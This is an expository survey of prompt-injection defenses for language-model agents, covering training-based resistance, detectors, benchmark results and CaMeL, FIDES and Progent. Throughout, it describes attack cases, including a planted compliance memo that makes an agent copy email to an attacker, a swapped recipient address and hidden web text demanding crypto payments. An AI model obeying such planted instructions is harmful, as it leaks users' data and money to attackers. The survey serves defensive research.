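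That model completed only 15.5 percent of the tasks in AgentDojo, a set of tests for agents that use tools. Putting about half of the planted instructions at the beginning of the data raised this to 84.5 percent. Attacks then succeeded 1.9 percent of the time, compared with 14.7 percent on the undefended model. *Defenses Against Prompt Attacks Learn Surface Heuristics* (2026) also links this kind of training to shortcuts that make models refuse harmless requests.

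Meta-SecAlign has been less effective against other attacks. Narisetty and colleagues cite a test in which adaptive attackers beat it 96 percent of the time. *Defusing Explosive Prompts* (2026) reports that Meta-SecAlign stopped every planted instruction meant to take effect immediately, but that 11.8 percent of attacks succeeded when the instruction stayed inactive in the conversation history until the user sent another, harmless message. The delayed attack resembles second-order SQL injection, which also relies on misplaced trust in stored text.

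### Measuring the separation

Attack success rates depend on how good the attacks are. *Can LLMs Separate Instructions from Data?* (Zverev, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2024) instead uses harmless questions to measure the underlying confusion between instructions and data. In one example, the model has to judge whether a text about a product launch is positive or negative, and the text ends by asking what a group of crows is called. If the answer contains the word "murder", the model followed the request when it should have treated it as part of the text.

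The researchers put each question once among the instructions, where the model should answer it, and once in the data, where it should not. They then calculated two scores:

- Utility = questions answered when among the instructions ÷ all questions
- Separation = questions answered only when among the instructions ÷ questions answered when among the instructions

If a model answers 80 of 100 questions when they are in the instructions, its utility is 80 percent. If it also answers 60 of those 80 when they are in the data, it leaves 20 unanswered, so its separation is 20 ÷ 80, or 25 percent. The actual test had 9,160 examples and covered nine models.

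| Model and method | Separation | Utility |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4, no special measures | 20.8% | 83.3% |
| GPT-4, best prompt | 95.3% | 96.6% |
| Seven open models, no special measures | 37.5% | 67.8% |
| Seven open models, best prompt | 52.6% | 62.3% |
| Seven open models, extra training | 95.5% | 50.0% |

The scores without special measures probably understate the models' ability, because the test put the data in the user's message, which developers train models to follow. GPT-4 may also have had an advantage, since it helped write the test. Even with the best prompt, GPT-4 answered roughly 400 questions in the data despite an instruction not to. More capable models were not reliably better at this. GPT-3.5 scored 56.6 percent without special measures, well above GPT-4, perhaps because stronger models can more easily do both tasks at once.

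These models are old now, and the trade-off between separation and utility has improved. On the same set of questions, Meta-SecAlign's training reduced attack success on a larger Llama model from 99.7 to 4.0 percent and hardly affected utility. The result is impressive, but a website would still be unsafe if its database ran 4 percent of injected commands.

*ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) changes the model itself. A language model first turns each token into a list of numbers, called an embedding, and a word such as "send" normally has the same embedding wherever it appears. ASIDE takes these numbers in pairs and rotates each pair by 90 degrees if the token is data, so that (3, 1) becomes (−1, 3). The surrounding software chooses which tokens to rotate based on where they came from, so the wording of the text cannot affect the choice.

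In six models, ASIDE raised separation by 12.3 to 44.1 percentage points without any training on attacks. Average attack success fell from 14.7 to 4.9 percent on one test, but only from 45 to 36 percent on another. When the researchers removed the rotation from planted text, so that it had the same embeddings as instructions, the model followed it almost twice as often, so the rotation was responsible for much of the protection. All of these tests used a single exchange, not the long series of steps an agent takes. The models sometimes followed planted text even though every token carried a label that attackers could not forge.

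Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, offer an explanation for why labels fail in ordinary models. They trained simple classifiers to read from a model's internal state whether it was treating text as the user's, a tool's or its own. The training data put identical web text under each label, so the classifiers could learn only the effect of the labels. The researchers then took users' messages from 200 real conversations and labelled them as tool output. In four open models, the classifiers still gave an average probability of 76 to 88 percent that the model was treating this text as the user's.

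The models seemed to identify the speaker mainly by how the text sounded. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak a file, the success rate rose from 2 percent for the commands that registered least as the user's to 70 percent for those that registered most. Ye and colleagues conclude that current models resist familiar attacks because they have memorised them, not because they can identify where the text came from. If so, part of what looks like separation inside a model is detection, which is usually weak against new wording. Ye and colleagues did not test ASIDE, which might do better because its labels affect every token.

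### Adding a meeting to a calendar

Even perfect separation would not settle what to do when a user wants an email to cause an action. Narisetty and colleagues give the example of a user who tells an agent to read an email and, if it is a meeting request, add it to the calendar. The agent has to use the email's content both to decide whether to act and to fill in the details.

Data can affect the result of a parameterized query too. What Maria types on a login page decides whether she gets in. But the programmer has already fixed the comparison that the database will make, and the database doesn't have to interpret free text to make it. A developer could treat the calendar task in a similar way:

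1. Before the model reads the email, the program fixes the only possible action, which is to add one entry with a title, a date and a time.
2. The model reads the email and returns either "no meeting" or those three values.
3. The program checks that the date and time are valid, then adds the entry.

If the email tells the model to forward the user's messages to a stranger, nothing happens, because the program does not include that action. But the sender still controls whether a calendar entry appears and what it says. They may not even need prompt injection, because a stranger can send an ordinary request for a meeting that the user never agreed to, and the agent will add it, following the user's instructions. The entry's title can also contain an instruction for an agent to read later. Narisetty and colleagues' tests included an attack in the description of a calendar event, though the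 agent that read it did not follow it.

A false calendar entry is usually a nuisance, but the same design is riskier when the agent handles the landlord's notices. The program can limit the agent to changing the rent payment, but the amount still has to come from the notice, so a forged notice can increase the payment. A limit on increases would reduce the damage if the user knew what limit to set. If the user asks the agent to deal with whatever is in the inbox, nobody can list the right actions in advance.

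An agent may also need to ignore a sentence in one task and act on the same sentence in another. *Can LLMs Separate Instructions from Data?* gives the example of a user who asks an email agent to summarise some messages. In one of them, a colleague, Daniel, asks the recipient to send back an email with the subject "Confirm". The agent sends it, which is a mistake, although Daniel meant no harm. If the user had asked the agent to answer routine messages, sending the confirmation would have been correct. Text in a parameterized query is a value because of where the programmer put it, but how an agent should treat Daniel's sentence depends on what the user wants, which the user may not have fully explained.

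The argument from history is therefore strongest for tasks where someone can fix the possible actions before the agent reads anything untrusted, and where a false value would do little harm. For other tasks, systems usually ask the user to approve each action. Narisetty and colleagues warn that attackers can deceive the user as well, and that people who see many approval requests stop reading them. Microsoft Office relied on similar approval for macros, and criminals spent years persuading people to click "Enable Content".

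## Classifiers that screen what language model agents read

Instead of asking the user to approve each action, a developer can have a detector scan every email, web page or file the agent reads and block or remove anything that looks like a planted instruction. Such detectors are already in commercial use. Microsoft, for example, connects one called Prompt Shields to its Defender for Cloud security service, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*. Some detectors have caught nearly every attack in a standard test, but others have missed the same disguised document hundreds of times in a row.

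### Four kinds of detector

*Text rules* look for words and phrases common in known attacks. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (Munirathinam, 2026) tested the rules from prompt-shield, its author's open-source detector, on 8,276 attacks from three public collections. The rules caught about 92 percent of the attacks that openly told the model to ignore its instructions, but only 35 to 45 percent of subtler attacks without such phrases.

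A *small trained classifier* scores the text instead of looking for fixed phrases. Meta's Prompt Guard 2 comes in versions with 22 million and 86 million parameters, the adjustable numbers in a model. Both are far smaller than the models that run agents, so they take little computing power to run.

A developer can also ask a *second language model* whether the text contains an instruction that does not belong there. This model can read the user's request as well, which helps when an instruction is suspicious only because it is unrelated to the task.

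A *probe* examines the agent's own model while it processes the text. Damianakis and Psounis (2026) list two examples in *SoK*: TaskTracker, which reads the model's activations (the numbers it computes internally), and Attention Tracker, which reads the model's attention, or how strongly it draws on each part of its input. A probe can look for the shift in attention that an attack causes, which Wang, Li and colleagues (2026) describe in *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* as a move away from the developer's instructions and towards the planted text.

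| Detector | Where it sits | What it can see |
|---|---|---|
| Text rules | Between a source of text and the agent | The wording |
| Small trained classifier | Between a source of text and the agent | The wording, judged by its training examples |
| Second language model | Between a source of text and the agent | The wording and, if the developer includes it, the user's request |
| Probe | In the software that runs the agent's model | How the model responds to the text |

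Rules, classifiers and judges can check only the text that developers send them. Leong (2026) points out in *Injection-Execution Dissociation* that companies usually place classifiers such as Llama Guard where the user's message comes in. A filter there does not check documents that the agent opens later, so it misses any instructions hidden in them. A probe can cover everything the model reads, but it needs access to the model's internals, which companies that rent a model over the internet do not have.

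### Where the antivirus comparison fails

Text rules work much like antivirus signatures, and both fail when the attacker changes the pattern. Anyone who knows only this kind of detector would expect prompt injection to repeat the history of malware.

Trained models improve on signatures because they can flag attacks that nobody has written down before. OpenAI released GPT-3.5 before the AgentDojo agent tests existed, yet as a judge it caught 84 percent of the tool results containing AgentDojo's attacks. Antivirus products gained a similar ability when they added trained classifiers.

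This ability to generalise has limits. One of Munirathinam's detectors looks for sudden changes in writing style. It scored perfectly on a set of artificial attacks but caught none of the 30 attacks in a new set of business documents.

In other ways, detecting planted text is harder than detecting viruses. A malicious program has to do something harmful when it runs, but planted text may contain nothing harmful in itself. A detector given only Daniel's email, for example, cannot determine whether the user would want the agent to send his confirmation. Text in a file also cannot stop a signature scanner from matching identical byte sequences, but a detector for agents is itself a language model, so an attacker can write text to mislead it as well as the agent.

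### PromptArmor on AgentDojo

The strongest published results for a judge come from Shi, Zhu and colleagues (2025), in *PromptArmor*. Their system uses an ordinary language model with no extra training:

1. The agent calls a tool, for example one that fetches recent bank transactions.
2. Before the agent sees the result, the judge reads it and decides whether it contains a planted instruction.
3. If it does, the judge quotes the instruction.
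4. Ordinary code finds the quoted words in the result and deletes them.
5. The agent reads what is left and continues the user's task.

AgentDojo has 97 user tasks in banking, travel, Slack and office work. Combining them with attackers' goals produces 629 attack cases. The researchers tried four standard wordings of each attack and counted the attack as successful if any of them worked. The agent used GPT-4.1 in every test.

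| Detector | Clean results wrongly flagged | Attacks missed | Attack success rate | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | – | 54.5% | 64.3% |
| GPT-4.1 as judge | 0.56% | 0.13% | 0.0% | 72.0% |
| o4-mini as judge | 0.34% | 0.47% | 0.08% | 76.4% |
| GPT-3.5 as judge | 11.2% | 15.7% | 6.8% | 51.4% |
| ProtectAI's trained classifier | 28.4% | 22.0% | 18.9% | 29.7% |
| DataSentinel, also trained | 0.1% | 48.8% | 38.6% | 46.4% |

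The agent completed more tasks with a good judge than with no defence, because deleting the planted text let it continue its work. It completed fewer than half as many with ProtectAI's classifier.

GPT-4.1 was both the agent and, in the second row, the judge. It did what the attackers wanted in more than half of the cases as the agent, but missed only about one contaminated result in 770 when judging. Evidently, a model can recognise an attack that it would follow if it were working on another task. Similarly, Leong found that coding agents often described a planted instruction as suspicious and carried it out anyway.

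These tests used well-known attack wordings, so Shi and colleagues also tried a program that kept rewriting its attacks based on what had worked. Its best attacks against the defended agent succeeded 0.34 percent of the time. With the defence removed, the same attacks succeeded only 37 percent of the time, compared with 70 percent for attacks the program had developed against an undefended agent. Text that gets past the judge may be less effective on the agent, which would be an advantage of this design. Alternatively, the program may have been poor at adapting its attacks to the defence.

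### A memo that small detectors missed

Leong tested a less conspicuous attack, in which an agent saves a malicious instruction to memory in one session and follows it in a later one. The attacker plants a fake internal compliance memo in a company's files, instructing staff to copy outgoing email to an external auditor. In the first session, the user asks the agent to save any compliance rules it finds. Two unrelated sessions follow, and the agent's conversation history is cleared each time. In the fourth session, the user asks for a status email, and a vulnerable agent sends a copy to the attacker.

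Leong ran this 40 times on each of nine open models, or 360 times for each defence. A classifier trained on a few dozen examples checked the memo each time and never removed it. A small language model acting as judge never flagged it either. Two filters on the user's message could not catch the memo, because it did not pass through them. The attack succeeded 88.9 percent of the time with each of these four defences and 88.6 percent of the time with none.

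The memo contained no conspicuous phrases, and its formal language resembled that of a real policy. A larger judge with 7 billion parameters also missed it every time. But when Leong showed the memo to Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, each flagged it in all 50 trials and raised no false alarms in 50 trials with harmless compliance documents. The trials used only one memo and ten harmless documents, and the judges were not protecting a working agent. Still, the results suggest that the small detectors failed because they were weak, and that detection can work against this kind of attack.

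One architectural defence, removing the tool that agents used to recall saved facts, did better in the main experiment, cutting attack success to zero in eight of the nine models. In a separate test, three other models got around this by finding the original memo again, and the attack succeeded in 32.5 to 97.5 percent of their runs.

### Attackers who know the detector

Defences look better than they are when tested on fixed collections of attacks. Wang and colleagues reviewed 37 papers on attacks and found that 14 used automated search, yet researchers were still testing defences mainly on handwritten templates. Damianakis and Psounis compared public benchmarks with the entries in LLMail-Inject, a competition to attack an email agent, and found that competitors favoured techniques the benchmarks rarely include.

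In 2025 Nasr and colleagues found that adaptive attackers could defeat most of twelve published defences. Munirathinam cites this result as a warning against relying on a single detector. In a small example from Munirathinam's own work, one prompt-shield detector caught 19 of 20 attacks, then none of 20 once the attacker knew how it worked.

Combining detectors can help. Munirathinam designed 20 attacks to evade the writing-style detector. That detector missed all 20, but the full set of prompt-shield detectors caught them all. Without its trained classifier, the set caught 14. However, the attacks were designed to evade only one detector, and an adaptive attacker would try to evade all of them.

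### Success under repeated attempts

An attacker who fails once can usually try again. In late 2025 the security company Gray Swan measured how much repeated attempts helped against Claude Opus 4.5, then Anthropic's newest model. According to Anthropic's system card, the safety report published with a model, the test covered attacks on models that use tools. Gray Swan had chosen attacks that worked on several different models. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, they succeeded 4.7 percent of the time with one attempt, 33.6 percent with ten and 63 percent with a hundred.

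If every attempt had the same independent 4.7 percent chance, the probability of at least one success in *n* attempts would be

1 − (1 − 0.047)ⁿ.

This gives 38 percent for ten attempts and 99 percent for a hundred. The second figure is far above what Gray Swan measured, which suggests that in some cases the attack failed however often the attacker tried. Suppose, for illustration, that the attack never succeeds in 37 percent of cases, and that each attempt in the other 63 percent has a 7.5 percent chance of success.

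| Attempts | Measured | All cases alike | 37 percent of cases always resist |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38% | 34% |
| 100 | 63.0% | 99% | 63% |

The numbers in the last column fit the first and third rows by design, so only the middle row tests the idea, and it fits well. Real cases probably vary more gradually. The owner of a particular agent can learn little from a single average, because some tasks may be nearly safe while others fail after a dozen attempts.

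Opus 4.5 did better in coding. With extended thinking, in which the model reasons at length before acting, attacks succeeded 0.3 percent of the time with one attempt and 10 percent of the time with 200. If the attempts had been independent, the success rate with 200 would have been about 45 percent. The attacker could also improve the attack between attempts, which should have raised the 200-attempt rate.

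Those results measure the model's own resistance. Anthropic also tested agents that operate a computer through its screen, with and without extra safeguards. Without extended thinking, the safeguards cut the attack success rate against Opus 4.5 after 200 attempts from 28.6 to 14.3 percent. For the older Sonnet 4.5, the rate rose from 85.7 to 92.9 percent. All four percentages are multiples of one fourteenth, so the test probably had only 14 scenarios, and the rise for Sonnet may reflect just one of them. In the equivalent test of Opus 4.6 in February 2026, VentureBeat reports, safeguards cut the rate after 200 attempts from 78.6 to 57.1 percent. These safeguards helped against a persistent attacker, but not nearly enough to rely on.

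### Results for 2026 models

Later safeguards did much better in browsers. VentureBeat's *Anthropic’s browser agent got hijacked 31.5% of the time before safeguards engaged* gives per-attempt results for Claude Opus 4.8, released in May 2026. With thinking on, safeguards cut the attack success rate from 31.5 percent to 0.5 percent without changing the model. Anthropic's 2025 safeguards for its Chrome extension combined a detection classifier with a better system prompt, so the classifier may not account for all of the later reduction.

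By July, Claude Opus 5 had reached zero percent across 129 browser scenarios, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. Earlier Claude models had come close to perfect scores on the test behind the 2025 figures, so Anthropic adopted a newer one with 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks. TechFeed reports these results for it:

| Model | One attempt | 15 attempts |
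|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% |

The closest equivalents to the 2025 figures are in Digital Applied (2026), which gives adaptive attack success rates in coding of 0.41 percent for Claude Fable 5, released in June, and 2.09 percent for Opus 4.8, with 200 attempts per scenario. The attacks and the number of attempts differ from those in the 2025 test, so comparing the two tests doesn't show the size of the improvement. *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a review of the September model, reports a further improvement against instructions planted in outside content.

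OpenAI's models have also become hard to attack directly. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05 percent of direct attacks written by an automated attacker. When attacks came through tools and outside content, the three versions of GPT-5.6 failed on 2.94 to 3.77 percent of them.

Rates this low make prompt injection much less useful against one chosen victim, but they are less reassuring when many agents visit the same web page. If 100,000 agents read a page and 0.2 percent of them follow the instructions injected in it, the attacker controls 200 agents after one attempt on each.

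### Attacks on deployed agents

Researchers have repeatedly shown that attacks work on real products. Damianakis and Psounis list several vendor-confirmed exploits. EchoLeak, from 2025, could take data from Microsoft 365 Copilot without the victim clicking on anything. Another flaw that year let attackers run code through GitHub Copilot, a programming assistant, and a third exploit took over a user's account through a browser agent. Constantin (2026) reports in *AI agent security* that four research teams broke agents in four different ways within ten days in July 2026. Their targets included Claude for Chrome and an agent's stored memory.

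The security company Zscaler found websites with hidden text meant to make agents send cryptocurrency payments, according to *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026). The following month, *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reported that criminals were developing tools for such attacks.

Planted instructions are still rare on the web as a whole. Damianakis and Psounis cite a scan of 1.2 billion web addresses that found just over 12,000, or about one in 100,000. They also cite Google's finding that malicious ones rose by 32 percent between November 2025 and February 2026. Like the old lists of known viruses, these figures count hostile material without showing how often it worked. Criminals may find it easier to trick people with methods such as ClickFix, so the low number is not evidence that defences have succeeded.

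### False alarms and cost

Even a low rate of false alarms matters for an agent that reads a lot. With GPT-4.1 as the judge, PromptArmor wrongly flagged 0.56 percent of clean tool results. If errors are independent, an agent that reads 100 results has a 43 percent chance of at least one false alarm. With ProtectAI's classifier, the chance is 81 percent after five results. Because planted instructions are rare, most alarms on ordinary web pages would be false, as in the antivirus example.

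The harm from a false alarm depends on what the system does with the flagged text. PromptArmor deletes it, which could silently remove a colleague's legitimate request from an email. Asking the user instead would bring back the approval prompts that people stop reading. Texts that discuss prompt injection, as a security team's email might, are especially likely to cause false alarms. When Munirathinam added a detector that recognises reworded attacks, false alarms rose from 0.9 to 3.8 percent on 339 harmless texts that use the vocabulary of attacks.

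Large judges are also expensive. *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) gives a price of $8 per million input tokens. At that price, checking a 10,000-token web page costs 8 cents, and the agent has to wait for the answer. Smaller models can do the job for less money, but not if they are too small. Among the open Qwen3 models that Shi and colleagues tested, the 32-billion-parameter version did almost as well as GPT-4.1. The 0.6-billion-parameter version flagged 63 percent of clean results when it answered without reasoning, and missed 76 percent of attacks when it reasoned first.

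Architectural defences also have drawbacks. Wang and colleagues tested eight defences and found that those limiting an agent's actions could triple its running cost or make it refuse complex tasks. Text filters were cheaper to run but protected less well against sophisticated attacks. None of the eight combined strong, explainable security with high utility and little delay.

### What a detector adds

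The main practical advantage of a detector is that a company can add one to an existing agent without redesigning it. PromptArmor, for example, needs no changes to the agent or its model, and a developer can replace the judge when a better one comes out. A detector may be the only protection available in the short term for an agent that already handles email.

A detector can also prevent harm that involves no tool call. In David C's recruiter example, it could remove the hidden instruction before the model reads the CV. PromptArmor's results do not show how often this would work, because they come from AgentDojo, where attackers try to make agents act.

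Detectors also keep records that investigators need after an attack. An alarm can identify the hostile document and when it arrived, so staff can find out which other agents read it. Munirathinam's software detects a series of near misses from one source and then screens that source more strictly. In a test, ten texts that were suspicious, but not enough to block individually, caused it to block a later one. Someone who needs a hundred attempts against one company therefore risks discovery long before the last one, as blue-box users did when telephone companies checked their calls.

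This does not help if the attacker practises on a private copy of the detector or spreads the attempts across many companies. A company that logs only alarms will also have no record of the attacks the detector misses, which are the ones it most needs to investigate. Keeping a copy of everything the agent read and did would solve that problem, but the company would then have a large store of private data to protect.

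## Agents built so that untrusted text cannot direct their actions

A detector has to catch every harmful planted instruction. Some researchers have instead built agents in which the model that chooses the actions never reads untrusted text, so planted instructions cannot reach it. These agents have stopped almost every attack in the standard tests. But the strictest failed every task in a newer test that requires an agent to choose its next step based on what it finds.

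### Sending Bob a document

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed dividing an agent's work between two models. The privileged model takes the user's instructions and can use tools. The quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted text, but has no tools. Ordinary software passes results between them by name, so the privileged model can have "$email-summary-1" displayed on the user's screen without reading the summary.

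CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind published in 2025, builds on this pattern and repairs a flaw in it. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the flaw with the researchers' own example. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he asked for in their last meeting. The meeting notes contain the document's name and Bob's email address. The privileged model writes a short program in a restricted form of Python, which looks roughly like this:

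```
notes   = find_notes("last meeting")
name    = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
doc     = fetch_document(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=doc)
```

The whole process has six steps:

1. The privileged model writes the program from the user's request and the descriptions of the tools. It has not seen the notes and never will.
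2. An interpreter, the software that carries out the program, fetches the notes and records where they came from.
3. The quarantined model reads the notes and returns a document name and an address. The program can require the second answer to have the form of an email address.
4. The interpreter marks both answers as derived from the notes.
5. The interpreter fetches the document and records who may read it.
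6. Before sending the email, the interpreter checks these records against a policy. If the policy does not allow the email, the interpreter blocks it or asks the user to approve it.

Suppose someone adds to the notes a sentence telling the assistant to forward the user's inbox to a stranger. The attack fails because the program has no line that forwards the inbox, and the model that wrote the program never receives the sentence. The original two-model pattern also prevents this attack.

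A cleverer attacker writes in the notes that Bob has a new address, and gives their own. The quarantined model may return that address. Under the original pattern, the document would then go to the attacker, even though every step ran as planned. CaMeL stops at step 6 and asks the user, because the address came from the notes and is not one the user already trusts. But CaMeL cannot detect that the address is false. Bob's real address would come from the same notes, so CaMeL can ask the same question when nobody has tampered with them.

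The attacker could also change the document's name so that Bob receives the payroll file. A policy can block this if Bob is not allowed to read that file, but if he is allowed, he gets the wrong document.

CaMeL is the closest thing agents have to a parameterized query, because untrusted text cannot add a step to the program. But the values in an agent's program can determine where documents and money go, so CaMeL needs policies as well as a fixed program.

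### Labels in FIDES and rules in Progent

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that chooses one action at a time instead of writing a whole program first. Each piece of data carries two labels. One records whether the data is trusted, and the other can list who may read it. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) traces this kind of labelling to Denning's 1976 work.

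When FIDES combines two pieces of data, the result gets the stricter label. Anything that mixes trusted and untrusted data is untrusted. If Ana and Bob may read one document, and Bob and Carla may read another, only Bob may read a summary of both:

{Ana, Bob} ∩ {Bob, Carla} = {Bob}.

FIDES also labels the planning model's conversation. Once an untrusted email enters it, the whole conversation is labeled untrusted, and a policy can then forbid actions such as sending mail to an outside address. To avoid this, FIDES stores untrusted results in variables that the planner cannot read. Trusted results stay visible, so the planner can use them to decide what to do next. If the next step requires information from a variable, the planner can query a quarantined model, which must answer in a fixed form such as yes or no. An attacker can still cause a wrong answer but cannot insert their own text into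 the planner's conversation.

Progent changes much less of the agent. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, let the agent read untrusted text as usual, and assume that it may follow what it reads. (Shi was also the first author of the PromptArmor paper.) A separate program checks each tool call against a list of rules and blocks any call that no rule allows. In their example, a user asks the agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed:

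1. A language model writes the first rules from the user's request. The agent may only search for Alice's email.
2. The list says to summarise recent emails and post the summary to the user's Slack account. The model that writes the rules proposes permission to read emails, look up the account and post to Slack.
3. A solver, a program that settles logical questions exactly, finds that the new rules allow more than the old ones. The change therefore needs approval.
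4. The agent learns the user's Slack name, and the model proposes allowing posts only to that name. The solver finds that this allows less, so the change takes effect automatically.
5. One of the recent emails tells the agent to forward the inbox to a stranger. Even if this fools both models, permission to send email would allow more than before, and the approver can refuse it.

The approver can be a person or a setting that accepts or refuses every such request. In tests on AgentDojo, 6 percent of the changes needed approval.

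| | What the planning model reads | What the software checks before an action | What a developer has to change |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | The user's request and the tool descriptions | Where each value came from and who may read it | The whole agent |
| FIDES | The same, plus trusted results from tools | The labels on the data and the conversation | The planner |
| Progent | Everything | The tool's name and the values passed to it | Nothing inside the agent |

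Progent is the easiest to install, but it does not track where a value came from. This matters for Bob's document because the agent does not know his address at the start, so the first rules might allow an email to anyone. If the notes then give the attacker's address, the model could propose a rule that allows emails only to that address. The solver would correctly find that the new rule allows less than before, so the rule would take effect without approval.

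### Results on AgentDojo

Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL, using OpenAI's o3 model, completed 77 percent of AgentDojo's tasks under attack, compared with 84 percent for an undefended agent. It needed about 2.8 times as many tokens. FIDES stopped every attack when its policies were on. Under policy enforcement, it completed 8 percent more tasks than a simpler planner with GPT-4o, and 16 percent more with o1, a model that reasons before answering. The simpler planner was also restricted, so these gains do not show how much performance FIDES loses compared with an undefended agent. Shi and colleagues report that Progent cut attack success from 39.9 to 1.0 percent while keeping the agent useful.

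CaMeL's cost depends heavily on its policies. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, reran it with two newer models on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. Adding the two models' results together gives these totals, which leave out attack runs that did not finish:

| CaMeL's policies | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
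|---|---|---|
| Off | 66 of 96 | 5 of 622 |
| On | 36 of 96 | 0 of 588 |

Turning the policies on prevented a few attacks and reduced the number of completed tasks by almost half. The size of that reduction is uncertain because there were only 16 different tasks, although the two models each completed 18 of 48 with the policies on.

Most of the protection in this test came from the fixed program. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the 144 pairings of a task with an attack, the attack needed a step that a program for the user's task would never contain. For example, a program written to summarise recent payments would not send money. But AgentDojo's attacks are older than CaMeL. An adaptive attacker would target values such as Bob's address, which only the policies protect, so CaMeL without policies is probably less safe than these figures suggest.

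Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent independently, using a small open model, Qwen2.5-7B, for both the agent and the rules. They took eight tasks from each of three AgentDojo suites and ran everything three times.

| | No defence | Progent | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attack success, banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Attack success, Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Attack success, office work | 0% | 0% | 0% |
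| Attack success, average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| Tasks completed under attack | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

The model ignored the attacks in the office suite even without a defence, so the results there cannot show whether Progent works. In the other two suites, Progent reduced attack success from about 39 to 6 percent.

The adaptive attack described the malicious action as a harmless step that the user had already authorised. It was meant to persuade the model that writes the rules to allow the action, a weakness that *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) also identifies. Its lower success rate is less reassuring than it looks, since Narisetty and colleagues think the gentler wording probably made the agent itself less likely to obey. They did not try the harder test of an attack that uses only tools the rules already allow.

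With Progent, this agent also completed two-fifths fewer tasks, and each task needed about 15 times as many calls to the model. Shi and colleagues did not find such a drop in their tests. The difference may be because a small model is bad at writing rules.

### Why CaMeL failed every task in AgentDyn

In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) argue that AgentDojo makes these designs look better than they are. In one AgentDojo task, the agent must pay a bill in a named file, so it can plan in advance to read the file and then send the money. By their count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan along the way.

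They wrote 60 tasks that all do, involving shopping, GitHub and everyday errands, and combined them with attacks to make 560 test cases. The tasks take an average of seven steps, twice as many as AgentDojo's. Each also includes a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page that tells the customer to log in first. With GPT-4o as the agent, except in the last row, the results were:

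| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |
| Prompt Guard 2 | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |
| ProtectAI's classifier | 0% | 0.6% | 0.9% |
| Meta-SecAlign (its own model) | 55.0% | 53.4% | 9.0% |

Suppose a user asks an agent to buy a phone charger. CaMeL's privileged model writes a program that finds a charger, puts it in the basket and pays. At the checkout, the shop requires a login and emails a one-time code. An ordinary agent reads the page, opens the email and types in the code. CaMeL's program can do this only if the privileged model included those steps in advance, because that model cannot read the page to find out that they are needed. The same restriction keeps it from reading any instructions an attacker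 might have planted on the page.

Costa and colleagues would call these tasks *data dependent*, meaning that no single series of tool calls completes such a task for every possible tool output. Buying the charger is an example, because the right next step depends on what is on the shop's page.

CaMeL also completed no tasks with the three other models in the main comparison. Its perfect record against attacks there is uninformative, since an agent that completes no tasks gives an attacker little to hijack. Progent can change its rules during a task, but with so many tools it often gave the agent the wrong permissions, and these mistakes accumulated until it blocked almost every useful tool. DRIFT, which plans in advance like CaMeL but lets a second check approve departures from the plan, kept more than half of the undefended agent's performance.

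AgentDyn is also an extreme test, because all its tasks need replanning. The share of real tasks that do is presumably between 6 percent and 100 percent, and nobody seems to have measured it. Li and colleagues told the agents not to ask the user for confirmation, which removes a step that CaMeL and Progent both rely on. But confirmation alone would not have supplied the lines missing from CaMeL's program.

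The detectors did not do well either. ProtectAI's classifier treated the helpful instructions as attacks, and Prompt Guard 2 let many attacks through. Meta-SecAlign, a model trained to resist attacks, had the best balance between these two errors, although adaptive attackers can usually beat it.

Some researchers openly accept limits on what agents can do in exchange for security. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) quotes a paper by 11 researchers from organisations including IBM, Google and Microsoft. The paper's designs limit agents' actions "to explicitly prevent them from solving arbitrary tasks".

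### Longer programs and isolated workers

One response is to write a longer program that prepares for more situations. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) did this when they adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at its screen and clicking. Many of the surprises such an agent meets are predictable, such as a cookie banner or a browser that is already open, so the privileged model can plan for them, even though the agent seems to need a fresh look before every action. At each branch in the program, a quarantined model looks at the screen and answers a question, such as whether a cookie banner is visible. The privileged model's programs averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and 4 branches on AgentDojo.

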